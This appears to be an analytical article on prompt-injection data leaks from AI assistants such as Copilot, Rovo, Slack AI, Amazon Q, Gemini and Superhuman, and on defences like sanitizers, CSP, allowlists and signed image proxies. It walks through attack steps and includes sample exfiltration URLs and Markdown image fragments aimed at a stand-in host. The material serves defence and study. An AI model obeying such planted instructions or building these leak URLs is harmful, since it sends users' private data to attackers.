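The link in this demonstration contained a request for help identifying a picture at an address that included the key. The picture was a pretext, and loacker explains that the data left when Rovo tried to look at it. Varonis emphasises a Rovo tool called ResearchAgent, which can browse several websites in a row without asking the user. Both accounts describe a request by the assistant rather than a leak through a Markdown image.

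### Why it matters who sends the request

A better sanitizer or a stricter Content Security Policy could have stopped only SearchLeak, because the requests in the other three leaks didn't depend on what the browser displayed. Switching off the assistant's web access would have stopped those three fetch leaks but not SearchLeak, where the assistant had no internet access, according to Varonis.

Varonis concludes from this that Willison's lethal trifecta doesn't quite cover SearchLeak, because an assistant can leak data without direct access to the internet. But Willison already counts loading an image as outside communication, and the employee's browser did that for Copilot.

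The sender of the request also determines whether the victim can interrupt the attack. In Reprompt and CoSnitch, Copilot kept working after she closed the tab. In SearchLeak, her own browser had to display the tag, so closing the tab before the tag arrived should have prevented the leak. She would have had only a few seconds to do so, and the only sign of danger would have been a search she hadn't typed.

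All three fetch leaks remained open for months after Varonis reported them. The RovoBlast report was triaged and earned a $6,000 reward after 63 days, and the repair took another six months. Microsoft records no exploitation of CoSnitch, and Malwarebytes' *“Reprompt” attack lets attackers steal data from Microsoft Copilot* (2026) reports no evidence of real attacks with Reprompt. The Hacker News (2026) notes that the published accounts of RovoBlast mention no real victims, but that this doesn't establish that there were none. The requests would have been hard to identify afterwards, because an assistant that summarises web pages routinely opens outside addresses.

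### What the click costs the attacker

An attacker who relies on a link has to persuade someone to open it while they are signed in to the right assistant. The attack fails if nobody opens the message carrying the link, whereas EchoLeak's email could start a leak without being read. Employees who suspect the message can report it, and a security team can then search other mailboxes for the same link.

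The victim is easier to persuade than in most phishing, though, because the attacker doesn't have to imitate a website, ask for a password or get her to install anything. He can send the link by email or chat, or print it as a QR code. The question runs when she clicks, so he also gains control over timing, which makes short-lived security codes worth stealing.

Requiring a click does very little to limit a leak once the user has clicked. The assistant works with the user's permissions, so what could leak depends on her job and on which services she or her employer has connected. None of these attacks needed a second approval before private data went into an outside address. Rovo's page didn't warn the user or show that a link had supplied the question.

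The effects can also outlast the session. Varonis got Copilot to save an attacker's instructions in its memory, a store of notes that Copilot uses in later conversations. The instructions would stay there until the user deleted them, even if she changed her password. In this test they came from a web page that the user had asked Copilot to summarise, but Varonis says a prompt in a CoSnitch link could also write to memory. This may be why Microsoft gave CoSnitch a severity score of 8.8, compared with its disputed 6.5 for SearchLeak. Both scores take the click into account, but the higher one reflects a high loss of integrity and availability as well as confidentiality. Microsoft doesn't explain those values.

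An employer can reduce the damage by limiting what the assistant can access. Varonis recommends disconnecting unused services and keeping legal, financial and personnel files where Rovo can't access them. It also warns that companies can't fully uninstall Rovo. According to The Hacker News, they can block it for individual apps, but on a site with several Jira products, Rovo's search and chat stay available until the administrator blocks it for all of them.

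### Filling in the question without running it

The simplest fix is to let a link put a question in the input box but require the user to press Enter to send it. Links from colleagues or help pages still work, with one extra keystroke.

CoSnitch is good evidence that blocking automatic execution stops the one-click version of the attack. When the link contained only `q`, the prompt appeared in the box but did not run. However, a forgotten second parameter was enough to undo this protection, so a vendor has to find every way a link can start a prompt, including old ones its staff may believe they have disabled. Atlassian's repair also targeted automatic execution. After the July fix, loacker confirmed that the crafted links no longer inserted and ran an attacker's instructions.

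Requiring the user to press Enter before the prompt runs adds a second step, but some people will press it because the text appears in a product they trust. Varonis advises users to read a pre-filled prompt before running it, which works if the prompt openly asks for passwords. But Reprompt's opening text looked like a muddled puzzle about a bird, and the requests for personal details came later from the attacker's server. An attacker could also begin with a sensible question and put the harmful instructions below the visible part of the box.

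A clear notice would help, such as "This question came from a link. Read it before you send it." The vendor could also block the assistant from using mailboxes, files and web requests to answer a question from a link until the user allows it. This would be awkward for a product like Enterprise Search, whose purpose is to search those sources, but such a product could treat the text in the link strictly as search terms.

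None of these changes affects instructions that arrive by another route. In PromptArmor's attack on Rovo, the user uploads a document with hidden instructions and asks for help organising her Jira tickets. Rovo adds the tickets to an outside web address and opens it. This happens even if the company has switched off web search, because a separate tool opens the address. The Hacker News could not confirm a fix for that attack as of 8 August 2026, a month after Atlassian repaired the link.

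## How much does it help if the user must click a link in the answer?

An ordinary link in an answer sends nothing until the user clicks it, even if its address already contains private data. The user can therefore still prevent the leak after the assistant has followed the attacker's instructions, which EchoLeak's victim could not do. How much this helps depends on how often people click, which researchers have measured mostly for links in email.

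### Slack AI

PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* describes a developer who keeps an API key in a private Slack channel of which she is the only member. The attacker has an account in the same company's Slack workspace but can't open that channel. He creates a public channel, where he is also the only member, and posts a message containing instructions. The data then leaves in four steps:

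1. The developer asks Slack AI for her API key.
2. Slack AI searches her private channels and all public channels, including those she never joined, and retrieves both her message and the attacker's.
3. The model follows the attacker's instructions. It reports an error and offers a link that reads "click here to reauthenticate", with the key in the query string.
4. She clicks the link, and the attacker reads the key in his server's log.

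The attacker doesn't have to know the key, because he only tells the model where to put it. He was also hard to trace. Slack AI cited the developer's private channel as its source but not the attacker's channel, and his message didn't appear on the first page of search results. In a second test with a different question, the answer did cite the attacker's channel.

PromptArmor reported the flaw on 14 August 2024. Slack replied five days later that the evidence was insufficient and that all members of a workspace can search its public channels by design. The attacker's message was in a public channel, but the key was in a private one. Slack released a patch on 20 August, the day the research became public. Slack (2024) said that someone with an account in the same workspace could "phish users for certain data" in very limited circumstances, and that it had no evidence of unauthorised access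 to customer data. Slack didn't explain in the statement what the patch changed.

The attack required less of the victim than the word "phish" suggests. Clicking the link was enough to leak the key, because the key was already in the address. In most phishing for passwords, a victim who clicks still has to type the password into the page that opens.

The attacker might soon not have needed an account either. On the day of the report, Slack AI began to use uploaded files in its answers. PromptArmor had finished testing by then, but thought it highly likely that a PDF with hidden instructions would work if an employee uploaded it.

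### Amazon Q for Business

Rehberger had found a similar leak in the preview version of Amazon Q for Business, an assistant for company data. Embrace The Red's *AWS Fixes Data Exfiltration Attack Angle in Amazon Q for Business* describes a test in which the user asks the assistant to process a text file containing planted instructions. The assistant then displays a "Sign In" link whose address contains a summary of the user's messages.

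Rehberger reported this on 4 December 2023, and Amazon had deployed a fix worldwide by 29 December. After that, the product replaced URLs with "[URL not displayed]", much as Microsoft's chat product did at the time. Willison (2024) describes the fix as preventing the output of any links.

With this fix, Amazon didn't have to work out which links were hostile, but users could no longer follow a link from an answer to a source. The fix also works only if the software detects every link, which Microsoft's filter failed to do in the EchoLeak case.

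### The case for treating the click as protection

Some users won't click, so an attack that needs a click yields less per target than one that loads an image. It also leaves a visible link that the user can show to her security team, whereas she wouldn't notice a transparent single-pixel image.

Links are also harder to give up than images. An assistant that answers a question about parental leave should be able to link to the policy, partly so the employee can check the answer. Most answers lose little if the product blocks images from unknown servers. This difference may help explain why Google declined to fix the link leak in Gemini.

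These arguments assume the user has a fair chance of recognising a bad link. She can judge it only by its text, its address and the place where she found it.

### What the user can see

The attacker chooses the link's text, and the text doesn't have to resemble the address. The order number from the parcel example could leave through a link like this:

| What the user looks at | What she sees |
|---|---|
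| The answer | Sign in to continue |
| The address, with the number unchanged | `https://pictures.example/?ref=48213` |
| The address, with the number in base64 | `https://pictures.example/?ref=NDgyMTM=` |

On a computer, the user can hold the pointer over the link to see the address. In PromptArmor's test, this revealed the API key in readable form, so a careful developer could have recognised it. Base64 encoding would have made the key look like the codes that websites routinely put in their links.

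Many people can't reliably tell where an address leads. Albakry, Vaniea and Wolters (2020), in *What is this URL's Destination?*, showed 23 addresses to 1,929 people recruited online and asked which website each would open. Six addresses had a company's name in the domain, as in `profile.facebook.com`, and six had it in front of the domain, as in `facebook.profile.com`, which belongs to whoever owns profile.com. Participants averaged 5.2 correct answers out of 6 for the first kind and 1.2 for the second. Only 8.3% always chose the true domain. Experience helped only a little. The heaviest users of technology answered about 25% of the second kind correctly, and the group with the least coding experience about 16%.

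The survey also included two addresses with a second company's name in the query string, which is often the part that carries stolen data. About 76% of the answers gave the correct destination for one address and 81% for the other, so a query string confuses people less than a misleading domain does. But the researchers asked only about destinations. A person can know that a link leads to pictures.example and still not notice that it contains her order number.

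Two smaller findings suggest that the user probably won't look at the part of the link that carries the data. In an eye-tracking study, Ramkumar (2020) found that people judging whether addresses were safe relied most on the part that names the server. They spent more time on longer addresses, but only up to a point, so they may not examine a long string of encoded text for proportionally longer. Reynolds, Kumar and colleagues (2020), in *Measuring Identity Confusion with Uniform Resource Locators*, found that users are confident that they can identify a site from its address but are vulnerable to tricks that disguise its identity.

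### How often people click

The most carefully controlled figures come from a hospital system. Ho, Mirian and colleagues (2025), in *Understanding the Efficacy of Phishing Training in Practice*, analysed eight months of simulated phishing in 2023 at UC San Diego Health, with 19,789 employees. Each month, every employee received one fake phishing email, and the researchers counted a click on its link as a failure. The click rate depended heavily on the story in the email:

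| Subject of the email | Share of recipients who clicked |
|---|---|
| Outlook password | 1.8% |
| Account login | 1.9% |
| Shared document (Microsoft) | 9.0% |
| Traffic ticket | 18.6% |
| Dress code | 27.7% |
| Vacation policy | 30.8% |

The average click rate across the study's ten emails, weighted by the number of recipients, was about 12.7%. In the first month 9.7% of employees clicked, and by the eighth month 56% had clicked at least once, so a person who avoids one bad link may still click a later one.

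A larger set of records gives nearly the same average. *Breaking Bad Email Habits* (Hydari, Adjerid and colleagues, 2026) studied 192,840 simulated phishing emails that a research university sent to 19,341 staff and faculty between 2016 and early 2020. Recipients clicked in 12.5% of the emails and reported 5.6%. In campaigns that asked for a password and recorded the result, about 3% submitted one. The password figure covers only some of the campaigns, so the comparison is rough, but it suggests that many people who click on a phishing link stop before giving anything away. Stopping after the click doesn't help when the link's address already contains the data, because the click sends it.

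Training didn't reduce clicks much. The researchers randomly assigned employees at UC San Diego Health to one of four kinds of training, shown after a click, or to a control group that saw only an error page. The trained groups' click rate was 1.7 percentage points lower on average. Over half of the training sessions ended within ten seconds. These results are compatible with *Content, Nudges and Incentives* (Lain and Jost, 2024), a study of employees which argues that phishing is a problem of attention more than knowledge and that training helps by reminding people periodically.

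### From email to an assistant's answer

Employees could be more likely to click an attacker's link in an assistant's answer than in an email. They know that anyone can email them, and their employer has probably told them to be suspicious of links. An assistant's answer appears in a product their employer provides, seconds after they ask a question, and has no unfamiliar sender to put them on guard. The attacker can also make the link look like the only way to get what the employee asked for.

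The Slack AI and Amazon Q demonstrations both used a request to sign in, and phishing emails about passwords and logins were the least successful at UC San Diego Health. Such a request may be more convincing inside a work product than in an email, but an attacker could also use other lures, such as a link labeled "Full vacation policy" under an answer about vacation.

Users seem to click links in AI answers at lower rates. Pew Research Center's *Google users are less likely to click on links* covers the AI summaries that Google places above its search results, and draws on the browsing records of 900 American adults. The records cover nearly 69,000 searches in March 2025, according to The Decoder's *Pew finds that only 1 percent of users click a source link*. Users clicked a link inside the summary in 1% of visits to pages with a summary, according to a Pew passage quoted in Pixel Envy's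 *Google A.I. Summaries and Search Traffic*.

That 1% is a share of visits, so the share of people who ever click such a link could be much higher. The links in Google's summaries were also optional sources for an answer the user had already read, whereas in the Slack AI attack the answer was missing and the link appeared to be the way to get it. The click rate for an attacker's link is therefore probably higher than 1%, and the email figures could be too high or too low.

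### A warning before the link opens

After a user clicks a link, a product can show a page that displays the link's address and asks the user to confirm. *URL Inspection Tasks* (Lain, Nakatsuka and colleagues, 2025) compared this with small puzzles that make the user work with the address, such as retyping its domain. In the main part of the study, 1,573 Americans played employees who had to clear a mailbox of 11 legitimate and 3 phishing emails.

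| Help after a click | Phishing links opened | Legitimate links opened |
|---|---|---|
| None | 74.5% | 90.6% |
| Page asking for confirmation | 57.2% | 87.9% |
| Inspection task | 35.0% | 82.1% |

The rates in the first column are far above those in the field studies because participants were told to click the links in legitimate emails, and the researchers made the phishing addresses hard to spot. The differences between the rows are more informative than the rates themselves. Simple confirmation stopped under a quarter of the clicks that would otherwise have gone through, and the tasks stopped about half. The tasks took a median of 6 to 10 seconds each, and the researchers recommend using them sporadically.

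The tasks work by exposing a mismatch between where the user thinks a link goes and where it actually goes. All the phishing addresses in the study imitated a company the participant knew. A link in an assistant's answer might instead lead to an unfamiliar site that doesn't imitate any company. The user could then retype `pictures.example` correctly and continue without learning that the rest of the address contains her data.

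More information about a link can help users judge whether it is safe. *I Don't Need an Expert* (2021) tested reports that explain an address to ordinary users. Its 153 participants judged the safety of addresses with 93% accuracy when they had a full report and 65% when the software only highlighted the domain. To reveal a possible leak, such a report would have to show what the address contains, decoded where possible, next to the name of the site.

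### Expected loss with and without a click

How much a required click reduces the damage depends on whose data the links contain. The following figures are invented. Suppose an attacker gets an assistant to show a hostile answer once to each of N employees. In one version, the answer contains an image that loads automatically and leaks data every time. In the other, it contains a link that each employee has a 5% chance of clicking, independently of the others.

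If each answer contains different data, such as the employee's own correspondence, and each leak costs $10,000, the expected loss is:

N × probability of a leak × $10,000

If every answer contains the same secret, such as an API key that the whole team uses, the first leak does all the damage. With a cost of $1 million, the expected loss from the link is:

(1 − 0.95ᴺ) × $1,000,000

| Employees (N) | Own data, image | Own data, link | Shared key, image | Shared key, link |
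|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | $10,000 | $500 | $1,000,000 | $50,000 |
| 10 | $100,000 | $5,000 | $1,000,000 | $401,000 |
| 50 | $500,000 | $25,000 | $1,000,000 | $923,000 |
| 400 | $4,000,000 | $200,000 | $1,000,000 | Almost $1,000,000 |

When each employee's data is separate, requiring a click reduces the expected loss by 95%, however many employees there are. An attacker can offset this by reaching 20 times as many people. When employees share a key, requiring a click helps a great deal if only one person sees the link, but hardly at all if 400 do.

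The employees' decisions wouldn't be fully independent. If one of them reports the link and the company warns the rest, later clicks become less likely. An employee may also see the link repeatedly if the planted message stays where the assistant can find it. Repeated exposure raises the risk, but by less than a constant 5% chance per exposure would imply, because some people are more prone to clicking than others. Hydari and colleagues found that university employees who had clicked on one simulated email clicked on the next 20% of the time, compared with 9% for those who hadn't, and that most of this gap reflected lasting differences between people.

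The Slack AI attack resembles the first row of the table, since only the developer could retrieve the key from her private channel. Needing her click was a real obstacle, but an attacker with one target can also study her and write a more persuasive link. The click rates at UC San Diego Health, which ranged from 1.8% to 30.8%, show how much the wording might matter.

### How vendors have responded

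Vendors haven't agreed on how much a required click reduces the risk. Amazon removed all links within a month of the report, Slack patched its assistant after first rejecting the evidence, and Google left Gemini's links in place. Microsoft removed working links from Copilot's Mermaid diagrams, which are still useful without them.

A researcher's chance of being paid for such a finding also varies. In 2025 Rehberger wrote in Embrace The Red's *Amazon Q Developer* that Amazon's cloud division, AWS, had no public bug bounty programme (a standing offer of rewards for reported flaws). He also had to wait several days before the company would accept a flaw in one of its AI products through its reporting channel.

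A vendor that relies on the click needs to be sure that a person will make it, because link previews and email software can send the request first. In two early months of a phishing study at UC San Diego Health, a misconfigured setting let Microsoft's software open links in some of the simulated phishing emails, and Ho and colleagues removed those visits from their data. If an employee forwards an assistant's answer by email, similar software could open the link before any colleague reads the message.

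## How well do sanitizers and content security policies block the request?

A company can rely less on its users' judgement by controlling how its page handles the model's answer. A sanitizer can remove an image or link before the page displays it, and a Content Security Policy (CSP) can make the browser refuse to load an image. Neither depends on detecting the attacker's instructions, so both can still work after the model has followed them.

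### Five ways to display an answer

The options run roughly from strictest to loosest:

| How the product displays the answer | Requests it stops | Requests it misses | What users lose |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plain text only | Image loads and link clicks | Requests by other programs that receive the text later, such as a messaging app making a preview | Formatting, pictures and working links |
| Formatted text without outside images | Image loads | Link clicks | Pictures from the web |
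| Images from an allowlist of hosts | Image loads from all other hosts | Link clicks, and data that a listed host passes on | Pictures from unlisted sites |
| Images through a proxy that loads only signed addresses | Loads of any address the model made up | Link clicks, and loads of hostile addresses that the product has signed | Pictures the product hasn't signed |
| An isolated frame | A script's access to the rest of the page | Image loads and link clicks, unless the frame has further restrictions | Easy interaction between the answer and the rest of the app |

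Plain text protects the user only if the program displays it unchanged. Many programs turn anything that looks like a web address into a link, so a developer has to switch this off too.

Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* describes how Google stopped turning links and images into HTML in Generative AI Studio, part of its Vertex AI cloud service, after Rehberger reported a leak. Microsoft kept the text formatting in Bing Chat's answers but added a CSP in May 2023 that generally prevented images from loading, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*.

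An isolated frame is a page embedded in the main page, and the browser can block it from running scripts or reading the user's session. It suits content that a sanitizer would otherwise have to delete, such as a preview of a web page the model has written. Isolation alone doesn't stop the leak, because images in the frame still load. The frame needs its own CSP, which can be stricter than the main page's. For example, Reddy and Gujral recommend a policy that forbids all scripts in model output. A chat page needs scripts to work, so it couldn't use that policy, but a frame containing only the answer could.

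### Removing images from the parsed answer

A sanitizer has to interpret the answer exactly as the renderer will. The simplest way to ensure this is to let the renderer's own converter process the text, and to remove dangerous elements from the result:

1. A parser reads the Markdown and builds a tree, a structured description of the answer in which each paragraph, link and image is a separate node.
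2. The converter turns the tree into HTML elements. It draws any diagrams at this stage, with outside pictures disabled.
3. The sanitizer keeps the elements and attributes on a short list, such as paragraphs, lists and bold text, and deletes everything else.
4. The page displays the result without changing it again.

The alternative is to search the raw text for a pattern, such as an exclamation mark followed by square and round brackets. This is quick to write, and it catches the usual Markdown image. It fails on other notations, as Microsoft's filter did in EchoLeak:

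| What the model writes | Searching the raw text for the usual notation | Removing image elements after conversion |
|---|---|---|
| Usual Markdown image | Removes it | Removes it |
| Reference-style image | Misses it | Removes it |
| HTML image tag | Misses it | Removes it |
| Picture in a Mermaid diagram | Misses it | Removes it, if the diagram has been converted without loading the picture |
| Markdown image shown as an example in a code block | Removes it by mistake | Leaves it, since it's only text |

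The mistake in the last row would annoy a programmer who had asked how to write an image in Markdown.

ainoya.dev's *Rendering Markdown Images in LLM Apps?*, a developer's blog post, includes sample code that removes image nodes from the Markdown tree, and suggests an allowlist of hosts for products that need pictures. Working on the tree is much safer than searching the text, but there is a trap here as well. In the tree format of remark, a popular Markdown parser, a usual image and a reference-style image are different types of node. Code that deletes only the `image` type would leave `imageReference` in place and repeat Microsoft's mistake. After conversion to HTML, both are the same `img` element, which is why the sanitizer belongs after step 2.

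The list in step 3 should contain what is allowed. HTML has many ways to load a picture, including the background of a table cell and the still image for a video, and a developer listing forbidden elements would have to remember them all. Forgetting an element on a list of permitted ones only loses some formatting.

A browser can also start loading an image as soon as a script puts HTML into an ordinary page element, even if the element isn't visible yet. The sanitizer therefore has to work on an inert copy that a script can have the browser create, where nothing loads.

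### Cleaning an answer while it streams

When a product streams its answers, the sanitizer has to run before each screen update. SearchLeak showed that sanitizing only at the end is too late.

Cleaning each fragment separately isn't enough either. Suppose the model writes a reference-style image, and its two parts arrive a second apart:

```
Fragment 1:  Your parcel is due on Thursday. ![logo][1]
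Fragment 2:  [1]: https://pictures.example/logo.png?ref=48213
```

The two fragments form an image only when parsed together. The first has a label with no address, which a parser treats as plain text, and the second has an address that nothing in that fragment uses. The software therefore has to add each new fragment to everything received so far, parse and clean the whole text, and only then update the screen.

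Parsing everything again for each fragment takes more computing time as the answer gets longer. A developer can reduce the work by updating the screen only a few times per second, though this makes the text slightly jerkier.

### What the browser checks

Software has bugs, and a sanitizer may miss something. A CSP gives the browser a separate rule to apply. The company's server normally sends it in a header, a line of information that precedes the page. A policy for a chat page might look like this, with line breaks added for reading:

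```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'none';
  script-src 'self';
  style-src 'self';
  connect-src 'self';
  img-src 'self' https://images.assistant.example
```

Each line is a directive, which names a type of content and the places it may come from. `'self'` stands for the site the page came from, and `'none'` for nowhere. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard from the body that publishes many web standards, sets out how a browser applies such a policy. If the model's answer adds an image at `https://pictures.example/logo.png?ref=48213`, the browser does the following:

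1. It prepares a request and notes that it is for an image.
2. Before sending anything, it looks up `img-src`. If the policy had no `img-src`, it would use `default-src`.
3. It compares the address with the two permitted sources, finds no match and cancels the request. The server at pictures.example receives nothing.

If the address had matched and the server had redirected the request, the browser would have checked the new address too.

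How well a content security policy blocks the request depends on its directives. For images, `img-src` overrides `default-src`, so a policy with `default-src 'none'` and `img-src https:` allows images from every HTTPS site, including the attacker's. A web page can also ask the browser to fetch something in advance, and W3C notes that a policy without `default-src` always allows such requests. An answer containing the right HTML tag could use one to send data even if `img-src` were strict.

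The standard lets an entry in a content security policy specify a host and a path but not a query string, so a company can't allow its logo at `/logo.png` while blocking `/logo.png?ref=48213`.

### What a CSP leaves open

A CSP controls only the requests a browser makes from one page, so it couldn't stop the relays in EchoLeak and ReLeak. It also has no effect in a mobile app that displays the answer without a web page, or in the email program of a colleague who receives a copy.

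A content security policy (CSP) that restricts `img-src` and `default-src` also doesn't stop a click on an ordinary link. Those directives don't apply to navigation, which is when the browser leaves the page for another one. The standard allows navigation unless some other directive restricts it. People who work on the standard have long disagreed about whether that is a gap. In a mailing-list thread preserved in a message by Deian Stefan, one participant wrote that stopping exfiltration "has not been a goal of CSP" and gave navigation as an example. Another replied that it is a goal for the people who use CSP. In a later message, Artur Janc of Google quotes a developer who complained in October 2018 that an attacker with code on a page could still send data out by redirecting the page.

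The draft describes CSP as defence in depth, not a replacement for careful input checking and output encoding. CSP may be more effective against image leaks than that description suggests, since a policy that allows no outside hosts blocks the request however the image is written. For links, the sanitizer has to prevent the leak.

A company also has to remember to set a policy, and an application works without one. In December 2025, veganmosfet tested Dify, an open-source chatbot-building platform that organisations can run on their own servers, in *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*. The researcher used a Dify template to build a chatbot that answers from a collection of documents, and loaded two PDFs into it, one with hidden text. When a user asked about prompt engineering, the chatbot retrieved the hidden text. The model, GLM-4.6, then added a Markdown image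 whose address contained the user's name from the chat, and the name reached an outside server.

Dify's page displayed Markdown images from any domain, and no CSP limited them by default. The test leaked only a name, but the same method could have leaked anything else in the conversation. veganmosfet recommends a strong CSP or, ideally, no Markdown or HTML rendering. Each organisation that installs self-hosted software has to add the policy itself unless the developers change the default, and many won't know it is missing.

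### Can a stranger use an allowed host?

Companies tend to put a host on an allowlist because they trust its owner. But the attacker doesn't need the owner's cooperation if the host offers a service that strangers can use. Two questions test an entry better than the owner's name does:

- Can anyone make this host fetch an address?
- Can anyone outside the company read what this host receives, whether in a log, a form or a file?

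The answer to both has to be no for every service on the host. These published cases all fail the test:

| Product | Allowed host | What a stranger could do there |
|---|---|---|
| Google Bard | Any subdomain of google.com | Run a program that records requests |
| Superhuman | docs.google.com | Create a form that stores data from an address |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot (EchoLeak) | A Teams service | Make it fetch another address |
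| Microsoft 365 Copilot (SearchLeak) | Any subdomain of bing.com | Make image search fetch another address |

Google had limited images in Bard, the predecessor of Gemini, to its own domain. According to Willison, in *Hacking Google Bard*, the attacker could still receive the data at script.google.com by using Google Apps Script, a service for running small programs. The attacker's instructions were in a Google Doc shared with the victim.

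PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes a similar leak from an email program. The program's CSP blocked requests to unlisted sites but allowed docs.google.com, where anyone can create a form and read the answers. A Google Form's address can include prefilled answers. An email contained hidden instructions saying that the user must be able to give feedback on her search results through the attacker's form. The assistant added data from the results to the form's address and used it as the source of a Markdown image.

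When the browser tried to load the image, Google Forms stored the data as a submission. The attacker obtained the contents of dozens of emails, including financial, legal and medical information. Willison (2026) traces the flaw to the CSP rule and credits Superhuman with treating the report as urgent and fixing it.

PromptArmor's *Codex for Everything Exfiltrates Connected Data* describes a test in which the same form trick worked against Codex, OpenAI's agent. The user asked Codex to sort through her email, and one message contained the attacker's instructions. Codex didn't display that message while reviewing the inbox, so she had no chance to spot it. The emails that reached the attacker's form included legal correspondence and financial plans.

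A company's own servers can also let the request through. Many sites store and deliver their pictures through a group of servers called a content delivery network (CDN). In its advice on a leak from Notion's AI features, PromptArmor recommends making sure the image CDN can't act as an open redirect, a service that forwards visitors to any address. A browser that follows W3C's rules would check the redirect against the policy and block an unlisted site. CDNs that can fetch and resize a picture from any address are more dangerous, because the browser connects only to the CDN and can't check the other address against the policy.

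Wildcards make the test almost impossible to pass, because the domain's owner can later add another service without telling anyone who allowlists it. A good entry is a host that serves only pictures the company has uploaded and whose logs only the company can read. The model could still add `?ref=48213` to the address of such a picture, but the number would reach only the company's own log.

### Image proxies and signed addresses

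Some products need images from many sites. A proxy can fetch them, so the browser contacts only the proxy and the page's CSP needs only one entry for images. Without further checks, though, an attacker can use the proxy to relay stolen data to their own server.

*Data exfiltration via Markdown image tags*, a post by Archestra, which sells AI security software, suggests removing the query string from an address before the proxy fetches it, since a logo doesn't need one. The post argues that the attacker's server then never sees the address the model tried to build. This is true for `logo.png?ref=48213`, but an attacker can instead put the number in the path (`https://pictures.example/48213/logo.png`) or the host name (`https://48213.pictures.example/logo.png`), so removing the query string makes an attack only slightly harder.

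Signatures are a stronger defence. Reddy and Gujral propose a proxy that accepts an address only with a signature and an expiry time. One way to build it uses an HMAC, a short code that software computes from a message and a secret key:

signature = HMAC(key, address + expiry time)

When the product's server approves a picture, it computes the signature with a key and adds the signature to the picture's address on the page. The proxy repeats the calculation with the same key and fetches the picture only if the result matches the signature and the time limit hasn't passed. Changing one character of the address changes the result completely. The model doesn't have the key, so it can't put an order number into a signed address.

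Signing image addresses doesn't prevent the leak if the server signs every address it finds in the model's answer, because the attacker's address then gets a valid signature too. The server should sign only addresses that come from a source other than the answer, such as the company's own list of shop logos.

Signing images from incoming emails can let data leak, even if the server signs them before the model reads anything. An attacker could send an email with 36 pictures, one for each letter and digit, and the server would sign them all. The model could then leak the number 48213 by displaying the pictures for 4, 8, 2, 1 and 3 in turn, much as Ayush Paul led Claude through a website letter by letter. The proxy can prevent this by fetching and storing every picture when the email arrives, so that displaying one later sends no request to the attacker's server.

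The proxy may be able to reach company machines that outsiders can't, so it also needs protection against requests aimed at those machines. Reddy and Gujral advise blocking private network addresses and long chains of redirects, and limiting the size and duration of each download.

### What Microsoft and Google block

In July 2025, Microsoft distinguished probabilistic defences, such as a classifier or a warning in the prompt, which make an attack less likely to succeed, from deterministic defences, which guarantee that a particular attack fails whatever the model does. Microsoft prefers deterministic defences where possible. For example, after a report from Rehberger, it blocked the Markdown image leak deterministically and looked for variants. It took similar steps against "certain untrusted links", but didn't explain which ones. Where it can't block an effect, it asks for the user's consent.

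SearchLeak and ReLeak became public the following year, and both included an image leak from Microsoft 365 Copilot. Both leaks went through hosts that Microsoft's rule allowed, so they don't contradict the principle. A deterministic rule's guarantee applies only to the requests it covers, and Microsoft's rule covered fewer than its customers would have assumed.

Google has a simpler rule for images. According to its *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), Gemini's sanitizer identifies the addresses of external images and doesn't render the images. *The Trifecta*, by the security firm Tenable, supports this. While looking for flaws in Gemini, Tenable's researchers observed that it filtered or restricted Markdown images and other output that might leak data.

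Links are harder to block, since Google wants most of them to work. Gemini checks addresses with Safe Browsing, Google's service for detecting dangerous sites, and replaces suspicious ones with the words "suspicious link removed". Safe Browsing may not yet have flagged an attacker's new domain, which would fit with Checkmarx's finding that an ordinary link could still leak data when clicked.

Tenable also saw Gemini route links through a google.com address. In Colab, Google's online notebook for programmers, that address shows a page where the user must confirm before leaving. Embrace The Red found that the page appears only for sites outside Google. A link to an attacker's Google Form could therefore avoid it, although nobody has published a test of this.

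The more recent *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) lists URL sanitization among Gemini's deterministic defences. A central policy engine controls it, so staff can change a setting instead of retraining a model. They can also add a "point fix", such as a text pattern that blocks a newly reported attack. Such patterns make sense as a temporary measure on top of a proper sanitizer. Gavish doesn't mention a change to the rule on images.

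Sanitizers and content security policies don't affect requests made outside the display. Tenable got data out through Gemini's browsing tool by exploiting a flaw that Google has since fixed.

### The EchoLeak table of defences

Reddy and Gujral compare eight defences against the steps of EchoLeak. These are their entries for the steps that concern display, with a dash where they consider a defence not applicable:

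| Defence | Image that loads automatically | Relay on an allowed host | Zero-click leak as a whole |
|---|---|---|---|
| Marking outside text in the prompt | – | – | Fails |
| Internal sources by default | – | – | Fails |
| Output check with permitted formats | Fails | – | Fails |
| Allowlist or denylist of addresses | Fails | Blocks | Blocks |
| Strict CSP | Blocks | Blocks | Blocks |
| Signed image proxy | Blocks | Blocks | Blocks |
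| Human approval of outside content | Blocks | – | Blocks |
| Monitoring of outgoing data | – | – | Fails |

The table's entries are the authors' judgement. They describe the table as theoretical in its caption and write elsewhere in the paper that they ran no experiments, although they mention "our tests" in one sentence.

Defences that control the request do better than those that try to keep the model from writing it. This broad pattern is convincing, but several individual entries are doubtful.

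A strict CSP blocks the relay only if the relay isn't on its list of allowed origins. Reddy and Gujral advise allowing only first-party origins (the company's own), without wildcards. EchoLeak used Teams, which Microsoft owns, so a Microsoft engineer could follow this advice and still allow the relay.

The entries for the address list are hard to reconcile. EchoLeak needed an automatically loading image to leak data without a click, so a defence that doesn't block the image shouldn't stop the leak. A list that applies to images as well as links would block an image from an unlisted host, but it would not stop the Teams relay if Teams were on the list.

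The output check is underrated. Reddy and Gujral describe it as dropping disallowed images, and a check that permits no images would have blocked the one EchoLeak used. The output check fails only if its permitted formats include external images.

The entry for human approval overstates its protection. Approval blocks the leak only if the person refuses, and many participants in Lain and colleagues' experiment clicked through a confirmation page. The entry for the signed proxy is correct as long as the server doesn't sign addresses the model generates.

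### A configuration for an email assistant

Suppose a company is building an assistant that answers questions about a user's mailbox in a browser. It wants formatted answers, links to the emails behind them, and the logos of well-known shops. This configuration provides all three:

1. The server parses each answer, converts it to HTML and keeps only paragraphs, headings, lists, tables, bold and italic text, code and links. It repeats this on the full text so far before it sends each update to the browser.
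2. The only working links lead to emails in the user's own mailbox. The model refers to an email by a number, and the server builds the link after checking that the email exists. Any other link becomes plain text without its address.
3. The server adds logos, not the model. It chooses them from stored copies on `images.assistant.example` and signs their addresses.
4. Drafts, exported files and the mobile app use the same cleaned text. The page where developers read logs shows answers as raw text.
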